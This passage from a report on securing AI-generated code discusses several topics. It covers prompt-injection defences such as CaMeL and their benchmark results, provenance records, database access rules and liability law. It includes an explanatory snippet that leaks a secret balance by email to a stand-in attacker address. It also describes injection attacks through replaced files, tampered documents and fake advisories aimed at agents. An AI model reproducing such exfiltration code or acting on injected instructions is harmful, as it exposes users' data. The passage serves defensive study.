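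The main test of CaMeL was AgentDojo, a set of office, banking and travel tasks with planted attacks. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (Singh and Srinivasa, 2026) reports that CaMeL completed 77% of tasks, compared with 84% without a defence. Odersky and colleagues reproduce results for separate models, which show one successful attack in 963 trials with OpenAI's o4-mini and none with Gemini 2.5 Pro. However, Gemini completed only 1.4% of the travel tasks, so CaMeL can reduce task completion by much more than seven percentage points.

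*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports less favourable results from an independent rerun of CaMeL on the banking tasks with two newer models. With the policies on, CaMeL completed 37.5% of the tasks with either model, about half as many as with the policies off. It blocked every attack in the runs that finished, but many runs did not finish.

Fixing the plan in advance provided much of the protection, even without the policies. It was generally enough in 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, because the attack needed an action that the user's task would never include. The policies matter for the other third, but they make many legitimate tasks impossible, such as the secretary's email, where the treasurer's address really is on the website.

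Garby and colleagues also found gaps in the tracking. In this simplified version of their example, the bank balance is secret:

```
low, rich = True, True
if balance > 1000: low = False       # low now counts as secret
if low: rich = False                 # skipped, so rich still counts as public
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "The balance is over 1000")
```

If the balance is over 1,000, the third line never runs, so CaMeL does not mark `rich` as secret and allows the email. An attacker would first have to get such code into the plan, which is hard but sometimes possible when the planning model reads only the user's request. For a task that said to follow a file's instructions precisely, the planning model wrote a loop that could carry out whatever the file contained, and two attacks succeeded this way with the policies off.

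CaMeL checks each action only when the plan reaches it, so a long job can fail at the last step. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) checks the whole plan before it starts and has the model repair any violation. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapts the design to agents that click through ordinary programs on a screen. These agents kept up to 57% of their performance, but a malicious page could still push a legitimate plan into the branch the attacker wanted.

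Odersky and colleagues' system blocked all but one of 1,926 attacks in the AgentDojo benchmark. With o4-mini, it completed fewer tasks than CaMeL in all four areas, including 52.9% of workspace tasks compared with CaMeL's 81.4%, although they describe the two systems as comparably useful. CaMeL's restricted Python doesn't let a program define its own functions, so it suits short scripts but not whole websites.

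### Harm through permitted actions

In one of the banking tasks, the user tells the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes, but an attacker has replaced the file. Two of the 1,296 attempted attacks on Garby and colleagues' own system succeeded, and both used this trick. Knowing that the payment details came from the file does not help stop the attack, because the user said to use them. The only remedy at this level is to forbid such payments, which would also block legitimate ones.

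A program can also misuse data it needs. If the lawyer's script is allowed to read the contracts and email a summary to a colleague, a rule that approves the colleague's address does not check the summary's contents. Singh and Srinivasa showed this with an agent that sent a secret to an approved service along with an ordinary report.

Limiting what a program can do does not stop it from producing wrong results. The lawyer's script could run in a perfect sandbox, with no network access, and still overlook a missing clause. Odersky and colleagues state explicitly that their system does not prevent such errors.

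### Access rules in the database

The bookkeeper's website also causes harm through an action it has to be able to perform. It must read every client's invoices, so a sandbox around the whole site does nothing to stop it from showing one client's invoice to another. The limit has to apply to each visitor, and the database can enforce it beneath the generated code. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, the rule could look like this:

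```
create policy own_invoices on invoices
  for select using (client_id = current_client());
```

Here `current_client()` stands for a function, supplied by the hosting platform, that returns the logged-in client's number. The database applies the condition every time the site looks up an invoice. If client 17 asks for another client's invoice, the database returns nothing, even though the page still lacks the ownership check. The rule also covers any page an agent adds later that reads the same table.

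The rule above works only if the site connects to the database on the visitor's behalf. PostgreSQL doesn't apply these rules to administrators, so a generated server that uses an administrator's key gets every row. The rule also covers only reading, so changes to the data need rules too, as Palmer showed when he marked himself as a paying customer of a Lovable site.

Somebody still has to write the rules, and on the sites behind CVE-2025-48757 they were missing or too weak. A platform can reduce the danger of a missing rule by turning on row-level security for every new table. PostgreSQL then shows ordinary users no rows until a rule allows it. If the agent forgets the rule, the bookkeeper sees an empty page and asks for a repair. Without row-level security, the page would look normal while exposing data to people who shouldn't see it.

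The agent might make that repair with the rule `using (true)`, which lets everyone read every row in the table. The invoices would appear, so the bookkeeper would be satisfied. A platform can automatically detect such an open rule and, before publishing, ask the owner whether every visitor should see every invoice. It can't forbid these rules outright, because a shop needs one for its product list.

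## Recording how code was made and warning its owners of flaws

Containment reduces the harm a flaw can do, but the flaw stays in the program until somebody tells the owner about it. Suppose researchers discover next year that the model that wrote the bookkeeper's invoice site often leaves out ownership checks. The bookkeeper may not remember which model it was, and nothing in the code identifies it.

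### What a useful record holds

An agent could write a short record whenever it finishes a program. For the invoice site, it might look like this:

| Item | Example | Question it answers later |
|---|---|---|
| Request | "A website where clients can log in and see their invoices" | Did I ask for clients' invoices to be kept apart? |
| Model | The exact version, and the date | Does a warning about this model concern me? |
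| Tools | The agent's version and any add-ons | Did the agent use a tool that attackers had taken over? |
| Files and pages read | An old price list and a help page about PDFs | Could a hidden instruction or a bad example have affected the code? |
| Dependencies | The PDF library and its version | Does a new advisory apply? |
| Checks run | Opened invoice 1041 as its owner | Did anyone test for this flaw? |
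| Hash | A short code calculated from the program's files | Is this the program that is running now? |
| Approval | The bookkeeper, without reading the code | Who accepted it, and on what basis? |

The hash changes if anyone alters even one character of the files, so it ties the record to one exact version of the program.

*Agentic process evidence* (Kainan and Hershman, 2026) provides separate fields for the model requested and the model used, because the model a user selects isn't always the one that responds.

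The list of files matters because fixing the code may leave the cause in place. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (Jha et al., 2026) describes how a tampered document can lead an agent to write an insecure setting. If the owner takes the setting for an ordinary mistake and corrects it, the document can still cause a flaw in the next program.

The lawyer's script needs a much shorter record. If the lawyer saves the script with its results, the date, the model's name and a list of the contracts it read, someone can later check whether it missed any.

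### Labels, bills of materials and signed records

The simplest existing record is a label in a commit message, the note that a programmer attaches to a saved change. The Linux kernel's *AI Coding Assistants* asks contributors to label changes made with AI, and allows only a person to sign off on them. The label used to name the agent and model, but in summer 2026 the developers shortened it:

```
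before:  Assisted-by: Claude:claude-3-opus
after:   Assisted-by: LLM
```

Corbet (2026), who proposed the final wording on the kernel's mailing list, relayed the argument that naming models gave companies free advertising and added little useful information. On the same list, Carvalho Chehab (2026) quotes another developer's point that some contributors use unreleased models with secret names. At least one maintainer had been deleting the labels altogether. The shorter label may be enough for the kernel, which has human reviewers and its own advisories, but it would leave out the detail the bookkeeper needs to recognise a warning about a particular model.

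Cursor's *Agent Trace* (2026), a draft format from the company behind the code editor, records the origin of individual lines. In simplified form, an entry for the invoice page could look like this:

```
file:          invoices.py, lines 1 to 5
written by:    AI
model:         anthropic/claude-opus-4-5-20251101
conversation:  link to the session that produced the lines
hash:          9f2e8a1b
```

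The hash lets a tool identify the lines after someone moves them. The format deliberately excludes any judgment of the code's quality and does not specify where tools should store the records. In April 2026, *Agent Trace* (2026), an entry in Thoughtworks' guide to new technology, reported early interest from teams. An open-source tool called agentdiff already writes similar signed records for several agents, including an excerpt of the request.

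A software bill of materials lists a program's components in a form that other programs can read. *Building an Open AIBOM Standard in the Wild* (2025) names SPDX and CycloneDX as two widely adopted formats. For the invoice site, the list would include the PDF library, so a tool could compare it with advisories. But Kainan and Hershman note that these lists cannot show which agent session introduced a change or whether a person reviewed it. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026) proposes a longer list that adds the model, its instructions and any outside tools it connects to, but this is still a concept without a prototype.

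Signed build records, such as those following the SLSA standard, could show that the bookkeeper's server runs a program built from particular source files. Kainan and Hershman want to cover the earlier step, when the source files are written, by signing a record that links each commit to the agent sessions that produced it. If a tool later turned out to be malicious, a company could search for every session that used it and find the affected code. The company could also refuse to publish code without a valid record.

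The agent would have to be unable to change the logging software, since an agent that could edit the log could hide what it had done. Kainan and Hershman describe the parts of this system but don't report using it. Their employer, JFrog, sells software for storing packages, so it would benefit if companies adopted the idea. *Verifiable Agent Conversation Records* (Birkholz, Heldt and Steele, 2026) is a draft of a common format for signed session records from different companies' agents.

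### Recognising AI-written code without a label

People rarely label AI-written code, even when a project asks them to. *Perspective on AI and quantum open-source software* (2026) examined eight mainstream scientific projects that all ask contributors to disclose AI use. In the median project, 4.56% of pull requests in 2026 included a disclosure. In 11 quantum computing projects, only three of which ask for disclosure, the median was 0.43%. *Visible Adoption, Untracked Contribution* (2026) searched projects from three cohorts of a design course and found no commit in which an agent had automatically credited itself.

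Some projects tell agents not to credit the AI in commit messages. *What Open-Source Projects Tell Their Coding Agents* (2026) examined the instruction files that projects write for agents. Among projects with rules on commit messages, 7.4% forbid this credit and 3.5% require it.

Searching for the names of AI tools finds many irrelevant commits. *The AI Attribution Paradox* (2025) analysed 13,617 commits that mentioned such tools, and only 31% clearly credited AI with the work. Most of the others had messages like "add Copilot support".

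Khosravani and Mockus searched for four kinds of trace: an agent's own account, a standard phrase in the commit message, a tag added to the programmer's name, and a settings file. Each misses a lot of agent-written code. In another census, OpenAI's Codex had opened 814,522 pull requests, but Khosravani and Mockus found only 843 commits that bore its mark. When a project accepts a pull request, it often merges the individual commits into one, which can erase the agent's name. Claude Code showed the opposite pattern, with 850,157 commits but only 5,137 pull requests. Khosravani and Mockus call for a standard label for code written by agents.

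*Fingerprinting AI Coding Agents on GitHub* (Ghaleb, 2026) describes a classifier meant to identify which AI agent wrote a pull request. Ghaleb trained it on 33,580 pull requests from five agents, using 41 features such as the length of the description and the number of comments in the code. Its F1 score, which combines the share of its identifications that are correct with the share of each agent's pull requests it finds, was 97.2%.

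Codex raises this average because it supplied 65% of the pull requests and was easy to recognise. If each agent counts equally, the score falls to about 89%. The classifier recognised only 57% of Claude Code's pull requests and mistook most of the rest for the work of another agent, Devin.

Ghaleb suggests that projects could use the classifier to flag undisclosed AI code. But every pull request in the experiment came from an agent, so the result doesn't show that the classifier can tell agents from people. The classifier's most useful clue was how often commit messages ran to more than one line, and many one-off programs have no commit messages.

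*Open-Source Intelligence for Code Provenance* (2026) studies how to detect AI-written code from the code alone, so that reviewers can choose the checks that such code most often fails. The bookkeeper already knows that an AI wrote the site, but the model's version, the request and the files the agent read are much harder to recover afterwards. The agent should therefore record them while it works.

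### A record proves origin, not safety

Like build provenance, a record of this kind can't show that the code is safe. Kainan and Hershman note that a valid signature doesn't prove that the record is accurate or that it includes every session.

*From Agent Output to Authorized Transition* (2026) warns against treating a signed build record as proof that a person authorised the code. A record of human approval calls for particular caution, because most of Anthropic's testers approved a clearly dangerous command.

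A saved request is also a poor substitute for saved code, because running it again may produce a different program. A model usually chooses each piece of text partly at random, and each choice affects the later ones. A file or web page that the agent reads may also have changed, and the company may have replaced the model.

Small chances of a different choice add up over a long program. Suppose writing a program involves 500 choices, and a second run has a 99% chance of making each choice the same way if all the earlier ones matched. The chance of getting an identical program is 0.99^500, or about 0.7%. Most differences would be harmless, but in Deng and colleagues' tests, repeated runs sometimes differed in whether the code was secure. An owner who wants to investigate a flaw therefore needs the program that actually ran.

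### The privacy cost of keeping requests

In Kainan and Hershman's design, a full session log includes the request, the agent's replies, its reasoning, and the data that passed through its tools. For the lawyer's script, that data could include whole paragraphs of clients' contracts.

Such logs can leak. The Next Web reports that Lovable's security incidents in early 2026 exposed users' conversations with the AI, as well as source code and database passwords. According to Halborn, a security firm, an update in February accidentally reopened access to conversations in public projects. Lovable fixed this for new projects but not existing ones, and a second report of the problem was closed as a duplicate.

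In Kainan and Hershman's system, owners can delete the log for privacy reasons and still keep the signed record, though its summary of the task could itself contain something private. Slides from the IETF, which develops internet standards, describe removing a single private entry while keeping the rest of a session. For most one-off programs, it would be enough to keep the model's version, the dependencies and the hash for as long as the program exists, and to delete the conversation much sooner.

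### Why advisories miss one-off code

Advisories identify software by its published name and version, which the bookkeeper's own code lacks, but owners can still get warnings about their code's dependencies. Replit automatically compares each new CVE with the packages in its users' projects. Even when a flaw in generated code gets a CVE, package scanners may have nothing to match. Unpwned's *170 Lovable Apps Were Exposed. Here's What Standard Scanners Miss* (2026) reports that Dependabot and two other tools missed the flaw behind CVE-2025-48757, which was in the sites' access rules rather than in a package. Unpwned sells a competing service, but this explanation is sound.

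For AI-generated code, Jha and colleagues found no equivalent of the advisory system. They propose CVE-like reports that refer to a model's version and a type of prompt. Software that recognises similar code, even after edits, would then help find the affected programs.

### A proposed warning for the invoice page

The following invented example extends that proposal by having the owner's agent do the search:

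```
models:    ExampleModel 3.0 to 3.2
feature:   a page that opens a record by its number
flaw:      CWE-639, no check that the visitor may see the record
search:    find where the program looks up the record, then
           look for an ownership check before it shows the result
test:      log in as one client and request another client's record
repair:    refuse any record that the visitor may not see
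```

*Extracting Recurring Vulnerabilities from Black-Box LLM-Generated Software* (Kordonsky, Levi and colleagues, 2026) describes how an attacker could find a model's repeated mistakes by building a Feature-Security Table. Researchers could use the same method to find the mistakes this warning should describe.

The bookkeeper's agent would download the warning and use its saved records to find programs with the same feature. It would read their code and run the test on a copy of the site with two invented clients. If one client could open the other's invoice, the agent would explain the problem to the bookkeeper and suggest a repair. The search would run on the bookkeeper's computer, so the publisher of the warning would never need to see the code.

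This search requires judgment, unlike matching a version number. Suppose 1,000 programs have the feature, 200 of them have the flaw, and agents recognise 80% of the flawed programs but wrongly suspect 10% of the sound ones. They would suspect 240 programs, 80 of them wrongly, and miss 40 that have the flaw. The warning should include a test for the flaw, because running it would clear most of the wrongly suspected programs.

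The feature may matter more than which model wrote the code. Kahn and Hastings gave three chatbots the same tasks, and every script for sorting files used a folder name from its settings without checking whether it led outside the intended folder. A warning about only one of the chatbots would have missed the other two scripts. Agents should therefore search for the feature in every program, including those with no record of how they were made. Knowing the model's version would still help an owner with hundreds of programs decide which to check first, and help the AI company identify what to correct in the model. The version would matter more if someone had tampered with one particular model.

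One objection is that a public warning helps attackers. React's developers had a fix ready before they disclosed the flaw, but nobody can prepare repairs for programs they have never seen. Publishers could warn hosting companies first, which would protect many public sites but not private tools on office computers. Keeping the flaws secret wouldn't protect owners for long, since attackers could cheaply repeat Kordonsky and colleagues' experiments.

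A fake warning is a more serious danger because it could contain instructions for the agents that read it. Publishers should sign warnings, and agents should use them to learn what to look for, but should not run commands from them or change a program unasked.

### Platforms that rescan their customers' applications

A hosting company can warn owners of flaws without a record of how their code was made, because it has the code and their contact details. Lovable (2026) says that since June 2026 it has automatically scanned applications before their owners publish them. Business customers can also schedule regular, deeper scans, which can find flaws that nobody knew to look for when the application was published.

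The company can also pass on what outsiders find. Axios reports that after Red Access discovered exposed applications, Lovable asked for the findings so that the owners could hear about them directly. A platform could also run a test like Palmer's on every site it hosts. The problem with old conversations at Lovable shows that platforms need to fix old projects as well as new ones. Hosting companies can't rescan a program that runs only on its owner's laptop.

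### Repairing a program by generating it again

An owner could respond to a warning by asking a newer model to write the whole program again. This takes little work for a short script, and newer models write secure code more often. But the old flaw can return, as it did in about a quarter of Deng and colleagues' standard runs.

A new version may also change details that the original request never mentioned, such as how the site rounds a late fee. *Pinning Decisions Before Failure* (2026) studies executable records of the choices a prompt leaves open. For example, a test that checks the rounding would alert the bookkeeper if a new version rounded the fee differently. For a website that clients rely on, repairing one fault and running the saved tests is usually safer than replacing everything.

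Automatic repair needs extra care. Jha and colleagues cite research in which models fixed the security problems a scanner had found but gave some users more access than they should have. They also warn that an attacker who can trigger a repair may be able to influence the new code.

### Sharing rules and tests in place of code

Owners of different programs could still share a list of things that no such program should allow. The list for invoice sites might begin like this:

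```
a client cannot open another client's invoice
a client cannot change the amount on an invoice
a visitor who has logged out cannot open any invoice
```

Each owner's agent would turn the rules into tests for its own program. If one owner found a missing rule, adding it to the list would help every owner, much as a fix to a shared package does. The list would help with unstated rules, the largest cause of flaws in Deng and colleagues' audit. If experts spent 100 hours on a list for 10,000 owners, they would spend 36 seconds per owner, not counting the cost of running the tests.

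The rules would still need some adjustment. An accountant may need to open every client's invoices, and an agent that misunderstood this could write a test that passes when it should fail. If everyone relies on one list, they could also all miss something important that it omits.

### Pooling discoveries among defenders

In *Cybersecurity in the Age of Instant Software*, Schneier imagines AI agents that continuously scan commercial and custom software for flaws, fix them and share what they find. Sharing would spread the cost of defence. He also suggests a market in which everyone in the network pays whoever finds a flaw and prepares the fix.

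Much of the benefit Schneier describes comes from many people using the same software. The missing line that fixes one invoice page is useless to somebody whose page has a different design. Owners of one-off programs can share the pattern of a flaw and a test for it, but each owner's agent would then have to write its own repair. Schneier is less confident that AI will repair flaws as easily as it finds them, because a repair takes more testing and a better understanding of the whole program.

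One-off programs avoid an obstacle he sees for commercial software, where the vendor controls repairs and licence agreements would have to change. The bookkeeper can let an agent repair the invoice site at any time. But a network that could change thousands of programs automatically would be a very attractive target for attackers, so it would be safer to let it send warnings than install repairs.

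## Who is responsible when generated code does harm

Warnings and tests help only if somebody acts on them. Owners, platforms and AI companies are more likely to act if they would otherwise have to pay for the damage, and whether they have to pay depends largely on the law.

Suppose a physiotherapy clinic in the EU wants online booking. The receptionist describes it to a hosting platform's AI agent, which runs on another company's model, and the site is live by the afternoon. Like the invoice page, the site checks that a patient has logged in but not that the appointment belongs to that patient. Eight months later, someone tries each appointment number in turn and copies 2,000 patients' names, phone numbers and reasons for their visits. The patients could blame the receptionist, the clinic, the platform or the model's maker.

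### Data protection and the holder of the records

The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) puts most of the duty on the controller, the person or organisation that decides why and how to use personal data. Here the controller is the clinic, which must protect the records in proportion to the risk, and health data needs particular care. Once the clinic learns of the leak, it has 72 hours to tell the regulator, unless the leak is unlikely to put anyone at risk. In November 2025, the European Commission proposed extending this deadline to 96 hours. The clinic must also tell the patients if the risk to them is high.

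Patients can claim compensation, including for distress. The clinic would have to pay for a breach of the rules unless it could prove that it was in no way responsible for the harm. Saying that an AI wrote the code would not help much, because the clinic chose to put the site online unchecked.

The receptionist normally has no duties to the patients under the GDPR, because employees who handle data for their employer are not controllers. A self-employed physiotherapist who built the same site would be a controller. The GDPR does not cover purely personal activities, such as sorting family photographs.

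The platform is a processor, a company that handles data on a controller's behalf. It must secure its own systems and tell the clinic promptly about any breach it discovers. If the only fault is in the clinic's page, the platform can argue that it met these duties. That argument is weaker if the platform's own design left the database open, as on the Lovable sites.

The model's maker probably has no GDPR duty to the patients if it only supplied code and never handled their records. If the agent read the live database while it worked, its maker may have been a processor too. The clinic therefore bears most of the legal responsibility, although it probably understands the code least.

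### Claims for a defective product

Product liability lets an injured person claim compensation from a manufacturer without proving that it was careless. The European Parliament and Council's *Directive on liability for defective products* (2024) explicitly includes software, whether it runs on the user's device or on a remote server. According to a summary by the European Parliament, the directive applies to products placed on the market or put into service after 9 December 2026.

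Under the directive, someone who makes a product for their own use can be a manufacturer. The directive covers a product that nobody sells when someone first uses it in the course of a commercial activity. The clinic appears to meet both conditions. Someone who generates a script for family photographs meets only the first and is not liable.

Even so, the patients could not claim for the leak itself. The directive compensates only three kinds of damage:

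- death or injury, including medically recognised psychological harm
- damage to property, unless its owner uses it only for work
- destruction or corruption of data that nobody uses for work

The directive distinguishes destroyed data from leaked data, and a privacy infringement or a purely financial loss is not enough for a claim under it. A patient who became clinically depressed after the leak might have a claim, but the others would have to rely on the GDPR. If the lawyer's script overwrote a signed contract, the directive would offer no compensation because the file was for work. ActuIA's *Agents IA* (2026) notes the same limit for companies that sell AI agents under their own brand, which will be liable for harm to people but not for money that the agent loses.

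For damage it does cover, the directive favours the injured person. A security vulnerability can make a product defective, and the manufacturer's liability is not reduced when a criminal exploits the flaw. If the manufacturer fails to disclose relevant evidence, the court presumes that the product was defective, so the clinic has a reason to keep records of how its code was made. A manufacturer can avoid liability by proving that nobody could have discovered the defect with the knowledge available at the time, but this defence would fail for a missing ownership check because that flaw is well known.

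The clinic may also be liable for other people's code. The directive exempts open-source software that its developers supply outside a commercial activity. If a volunteer's library caused a patient's injury through the booking site, the patient could claim from the clinic but not from the volunteer.

### Is generated code a product?

The model's maker may share liability. The directive treats providers of AI systems as manufacturers, so a coding agent is itself a product. The maker of a defective component is liable alongside the maker of the finished product, and the injured person can claim the full amount from either.

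But according to the directive's introduction, "the mere source code of software" is information, not a product. The model's maker could argue that it supplied only source code. The clinic could reply that the agent delivered a running website, or that an agent that regularly leaves out access checks is itself defective. A component's maker can also avoid liability if the defect came from the customer's instructions, but the receptionist never told the agent to leave out the check. No court has settled this, because the new rules do not apply until 9 December.

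A site built before that date can come under the new rules if someone substantially modifies it later. Where no more specific product-safety rule applies, a modification is substantial if it changes the site's purpose or performance in a way the original risk assessment did not foresee, and so increases the risk. Adding treatment notes to the booking site could qualify. The release of a safer coding model next year would not by itself make this year's model defective.

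EU countries also have to write the directive into their own law. *Neue Produkthaftung* (Januschewsky, 2026) reported on 4 December that Austria's government had not yet put a bill before parliament. Until a country passes such a law, an injured person generally can't use the directive directly against a private company.

### The Cyber Resilience Act

The European Parliament and Council's *Cyber Resilience Act* (2024) sets security requirements that apply before anyone suffers harm. It covers only commercially supplied software and devices that can connect to other devices or networks. Its definition of a manufacturer is narrower than the directive's, because the manufacturer must market the product under its own name or trademark. The European Commission's *FAQs on the Cyber Resilience Act* (2025) confirm that the Act does not cover products made only for the maker's own use.

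The booking site is also outside the Act because people use it only through a browser. Addleshaw Goddard's *EU Cyber Resilience Act*, a law firm's summary of the Commission's final guidance, says that such web applications are not covered unless they support the functions of a covered product. Apps that people install are covered. Orrick's *EU Cyber Resilience Act* (2026) notes that this guidance, published on 27 July 2026, is not legally binding.

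If the clinic gave its patients an app to install, the Act would probably apply, even if the app was free. The requirements cover one-off products as well as series. The clinic would have to assess the risks, test the app regularly and deal with vulnerabilities, usually for at least five years. Since 11 September 2026, manufacturers have had to report vulnerabilities that attackers are exploiting. Most of the other duties start on 11 December 2027.

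The table shows how the three laws would probably apply to products first used after those dates:

| Program | GDPR | Product Liability Directive | Cyber Resilience Act |
|---|---|---|---|
| Script for family photographs | No | No | No |
| Lawyer's contract script | Yes, if the contracts contain personal data | Yes, but not for lost work files | No |
| Clinic's booking site | Yes | Yes, but not for the leak itself | No |
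| Clinic's app for patients to install | Yes | Yes, but not for the leak itself | Yes |

A coding agent that people install is a commercial product, so its maker has duties under the Act. It is less clear whether a secure agent must also write secure programs. If regulators decided that it must, they could take up a recurring flaw with the agent's maker instead of pursuing thousands of clinics.

The EU planned a separate law to make it easier to sue over harm from AI when somebody was at fault, but the Commission withdrew the proposal in 2025. *Is Europe Ready for Advanced AI?* (Jahangir, 2026) discusses the resulting gaps with Brando Benifei, a member of the European Parliament. *Von der Leyen’s centrist allies clash over AI liability rules* (Stanciuc, 2026) reports that lawmakers disagree about bringing such rules back.

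### Britain and the United States

Britain kept the GDPR's main duties after leaving the EU, so a British clinic would be in much the same position over the leak. In 2023 the Police Service of Northern Ireland mistakenly published a spreadsheet with a hidden sheet that listed all 9,483 of its officers and staff. The regulator fined the police force £750,000 but did not fine the maker of the spreadsheet program. It would have fined the force £5.6 million if it did not have a policy of reducing fines for public bodies.

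British product liability law is less clear about software than the new EU directive. The Consumer Protection Act 1987 defines a product as goods or electricity, so it is doubtful whether a downloaded program or a website counts. The Law Commission, which advises the government on legal reform, began a review of these rules in 2025. The government also published a voluntary code of practice that year on secure development for companies that sell software, but it is not aimed at a clinic that builds its own tool.

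The United States has no general federal law on software security or on liability for defective products, so a mix of federal and state rules would apply to an American clinic. HIPAA, a federal law, requires most healthcare providers to protect patients' records. Every state requires notice of certain data leaks, and the Federal Trade Commission can act against companies with unreasonably weak security. Suing the model's maker would be harder, because state courts have often doubted whether software is a product, and many reject negligence claims for purely financial losses.

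Law360's *Senate Panel Seeks To Hold AI Giants Liable For Rogue Hacks* reports that senators from both parties want civil and criminal liability for the makers and users of advanced models. The senators are concerned about misuse of these models, including cyberattacks by rogue agents, which is a different problem from a generated booking site that leaks data.

Official security guidance mostly treats AI-written code like any other code. The US standards institute NIST does not distinguish between them in its 2024 guidance on developing AI models, because it assumes that someone will check all source code for vulnerabilities before use. Nobody at the clinic could do that check. In *AI and Secure Code Generation*, Aitel and Geer (2025) similarly criticize current security frameworks for assuming predictable human programmers and clear accountability.

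In joint guidelines from 2023, British and American security agencies asked providers of AI components to take responsibility for the security of users further down the supply chain. The guidelines are not binding and mainly concern attacks on AI systems, but the same principle could apply to the code those systems write.

### What the tools' terms say

The companies' contracts make the customer responsible. OpenAI's 2025 consumer terms required users to evaluate output before relying on it, with human review where appropriate. They limited the company's liability to $100 or the amount the user had paid in the previous year, whichever was greater. GitHub's terms for Copilot left users responsible for any suggestions they put in their code. Lovable relied on a similar term when it disputed the CVE for its customers' open databases.

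The patients never agreed to these terms, and under the EU directive a contract can't remove an injured person's right to compensation. But a contract can still affect whether the clinic recovers its own losses from the platform or the model's maker.

AI companies can accept responsibility for output when customers demand it. Microsoft, OpenAI and Anthropic have promised to defend business customers against copyright claims over what their models produce. A similar promise covering well-known security flaws would give these companies a direct financial reason to prevent them.

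### Who should bear the cost

A common principle in the economics of law is to put liability on whoever can prevent the harm most cheaply. Suppose 30% of generated booking sites lack the ownership check, attackers exploit 5% of those, and each leak costs $20,000. The average loss is 0.3 × 0.05 × $20,000, or $300 per site. Each party could reduce it at a different price (all the numbers are invented):

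| Precaution | Cost per site | Flaws prevented | Loss avoided per site |
|---|---|---|---|
| The model's maker improves its training | $1 | 50% | $150 |
| The platform tests each site with two invented patients | $5 | 80% | $240 |
| The owner hires a reviewer | $200 | 90% | $270 |

Each precaution is worth its price if nobody else takes one. But if the model's maker and the platform both act, and the platform catches 80% of the flaws that remain, the average loss falls to $30. Hiring a reviewer would then cost $200 and reduce the average loss by only another $27. Making only the owner liable would encourage the most expensive precaution or, more likely, none, since most owners would not know they needed it.

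The argument for making the **model's maker** liable is that one improvement in training benefits every later program, and the company can pay for it. However, the maker does not know which rules each owner needs, and unstated rules of this kind were the largest cause of flaws in the audit of live applications. A company liable for every omission might make its agents refuse useful work, and people could switch to a free model whose developer is abroad or has no money. Limiting liability to well-known flaws that an agent can avoid by asking one question would answer much of this objection.

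A **hosting platform** can see the code, test the live site and block publication until the owner fixes a flaw. It can do this for as long as the site is online, while the model's maker may have no further contact with the program. But the lawyer's script never reaches a hosting platform, and strict liability could drive risky sites to hosts that check nothing. A platform can't always tell whether a page is public by mistake, so it has to ask the owner.

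The **owner** chose to collect the data, benefits from the program and knows who should see what. If owners had no liability, they would have little reason to answer the platform's questions or install repairs. Yet the clinic can't see the flaw and may not be able to pay for the harm. If each of the 2,000 patients won €500, the clinic would owe €1 million, and if it became insolvent, they would receive little. Compulsory insurance would help, and insurers could require the two-patient test before covering a site.

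Ji, Jun and colleagues (2024) argue in *Cybersecurity Risks of AI-Generated Code* that individual users should share the burden with AI developers, organisations that produce code at scale, and policymakers. The example supports this view. The owner should remain answerable to the patients but be able to recover the cost from the platform or the model's maker if a cheap standard test would have found the flaw. The receptionist, who has the least money and power of anyone involved, should not pay for an honest mistake.

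### Spreadsheets as a precedent

Organisations have relied on unreviewed programs before. A spreadsheet is a program whose code is its formulas, and an accountant or a manager usually writes it. Raymond Panko reported in a 2008 review that audits had found errors in 88% of 113 spreadsheets. Powell, Baker and Lawson (2009) examined 50 spreadsheets in use at organisations and found errors in roughly 1–2% of the formulas.

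These figures are compatible, because if each formula has a 1% chance of being wrong, a spreadsheet with 200 formulas has an 87% chance of containing at least one error. Most of these errors do little harm, so these error rates are not comparable with the share of generated applications that have a vulnerability.

Some do contribute to enormous losses. In 2012 the bank JPMorgan Chase lost about $6.2 billion on trades by its London office. The bank's own investigation found that staff had calculated a measure of the risk by copying figures between spreadsheets, and that one formula divided by a sum instead of an average:

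```
intended:   (new rate − old rate) / ((new rate + old rate) / 2)
entered:    (new rate − old rate) / (new rate + old rate)
```

If the rate rose from 100 to 110, the correct result would be 9.5%, but the spreadsheet would give 4.8%. The mistake halved the apparent volatility and made the trades look safer. It did not cause the loss alone, since managers had other warnings.

Banking regulators have responded to unreliable models and spreadsheets with rules about who keeps track of them. In guidance from 2011, US regulators told banks to keep an inventory of their models and have people other than the developers check them. Under rules in force since May 2024, British regulators ask large banks to rank models by risk and make a named senior manager responsible for the whole system. International standards from 2013 call for the largest banks to control the spreadsheets behind their risk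 figures.

The record of these rules is mixed. JPMorgan's loss came a year after the US guidance. Its reviewers had approved the new model knowing that it depended on manual spreadsheets, on the understanding that the bank would automate them. The bank never finished doing so. In 2023 the Basel Committee, which sets international banking standards, found that only two of 31 major banks fully met its 2013 principles. Those principles cover risk data in general, so the finding doesn't show how well banks control spreadsheets, but it does show that even rich, closely supervised companies struggle to follow such rules.

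The inventory would carry over best, because a coding agent or platform could list each program when it creates it, whereas banks have to find spreadsheets scattered across thousands of computers. Risk tiers would also work if they depended on what data a program holds and who can reach it. The lawyer's script might need only a sandbox and a backup, while the booking site would need a test for each access rule and a new review after every change.

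Each program that remains in use should also have a named owner who receives warnings and decides when to delete it. If the receptionist leaves, the clinic should have to name a new owner to keep the site online. Independent human review is the hardest practice to carry over, because there are too many programs and too few reviewers. The clinic could keep its inventory on one page but would still need the platform to run the tests.
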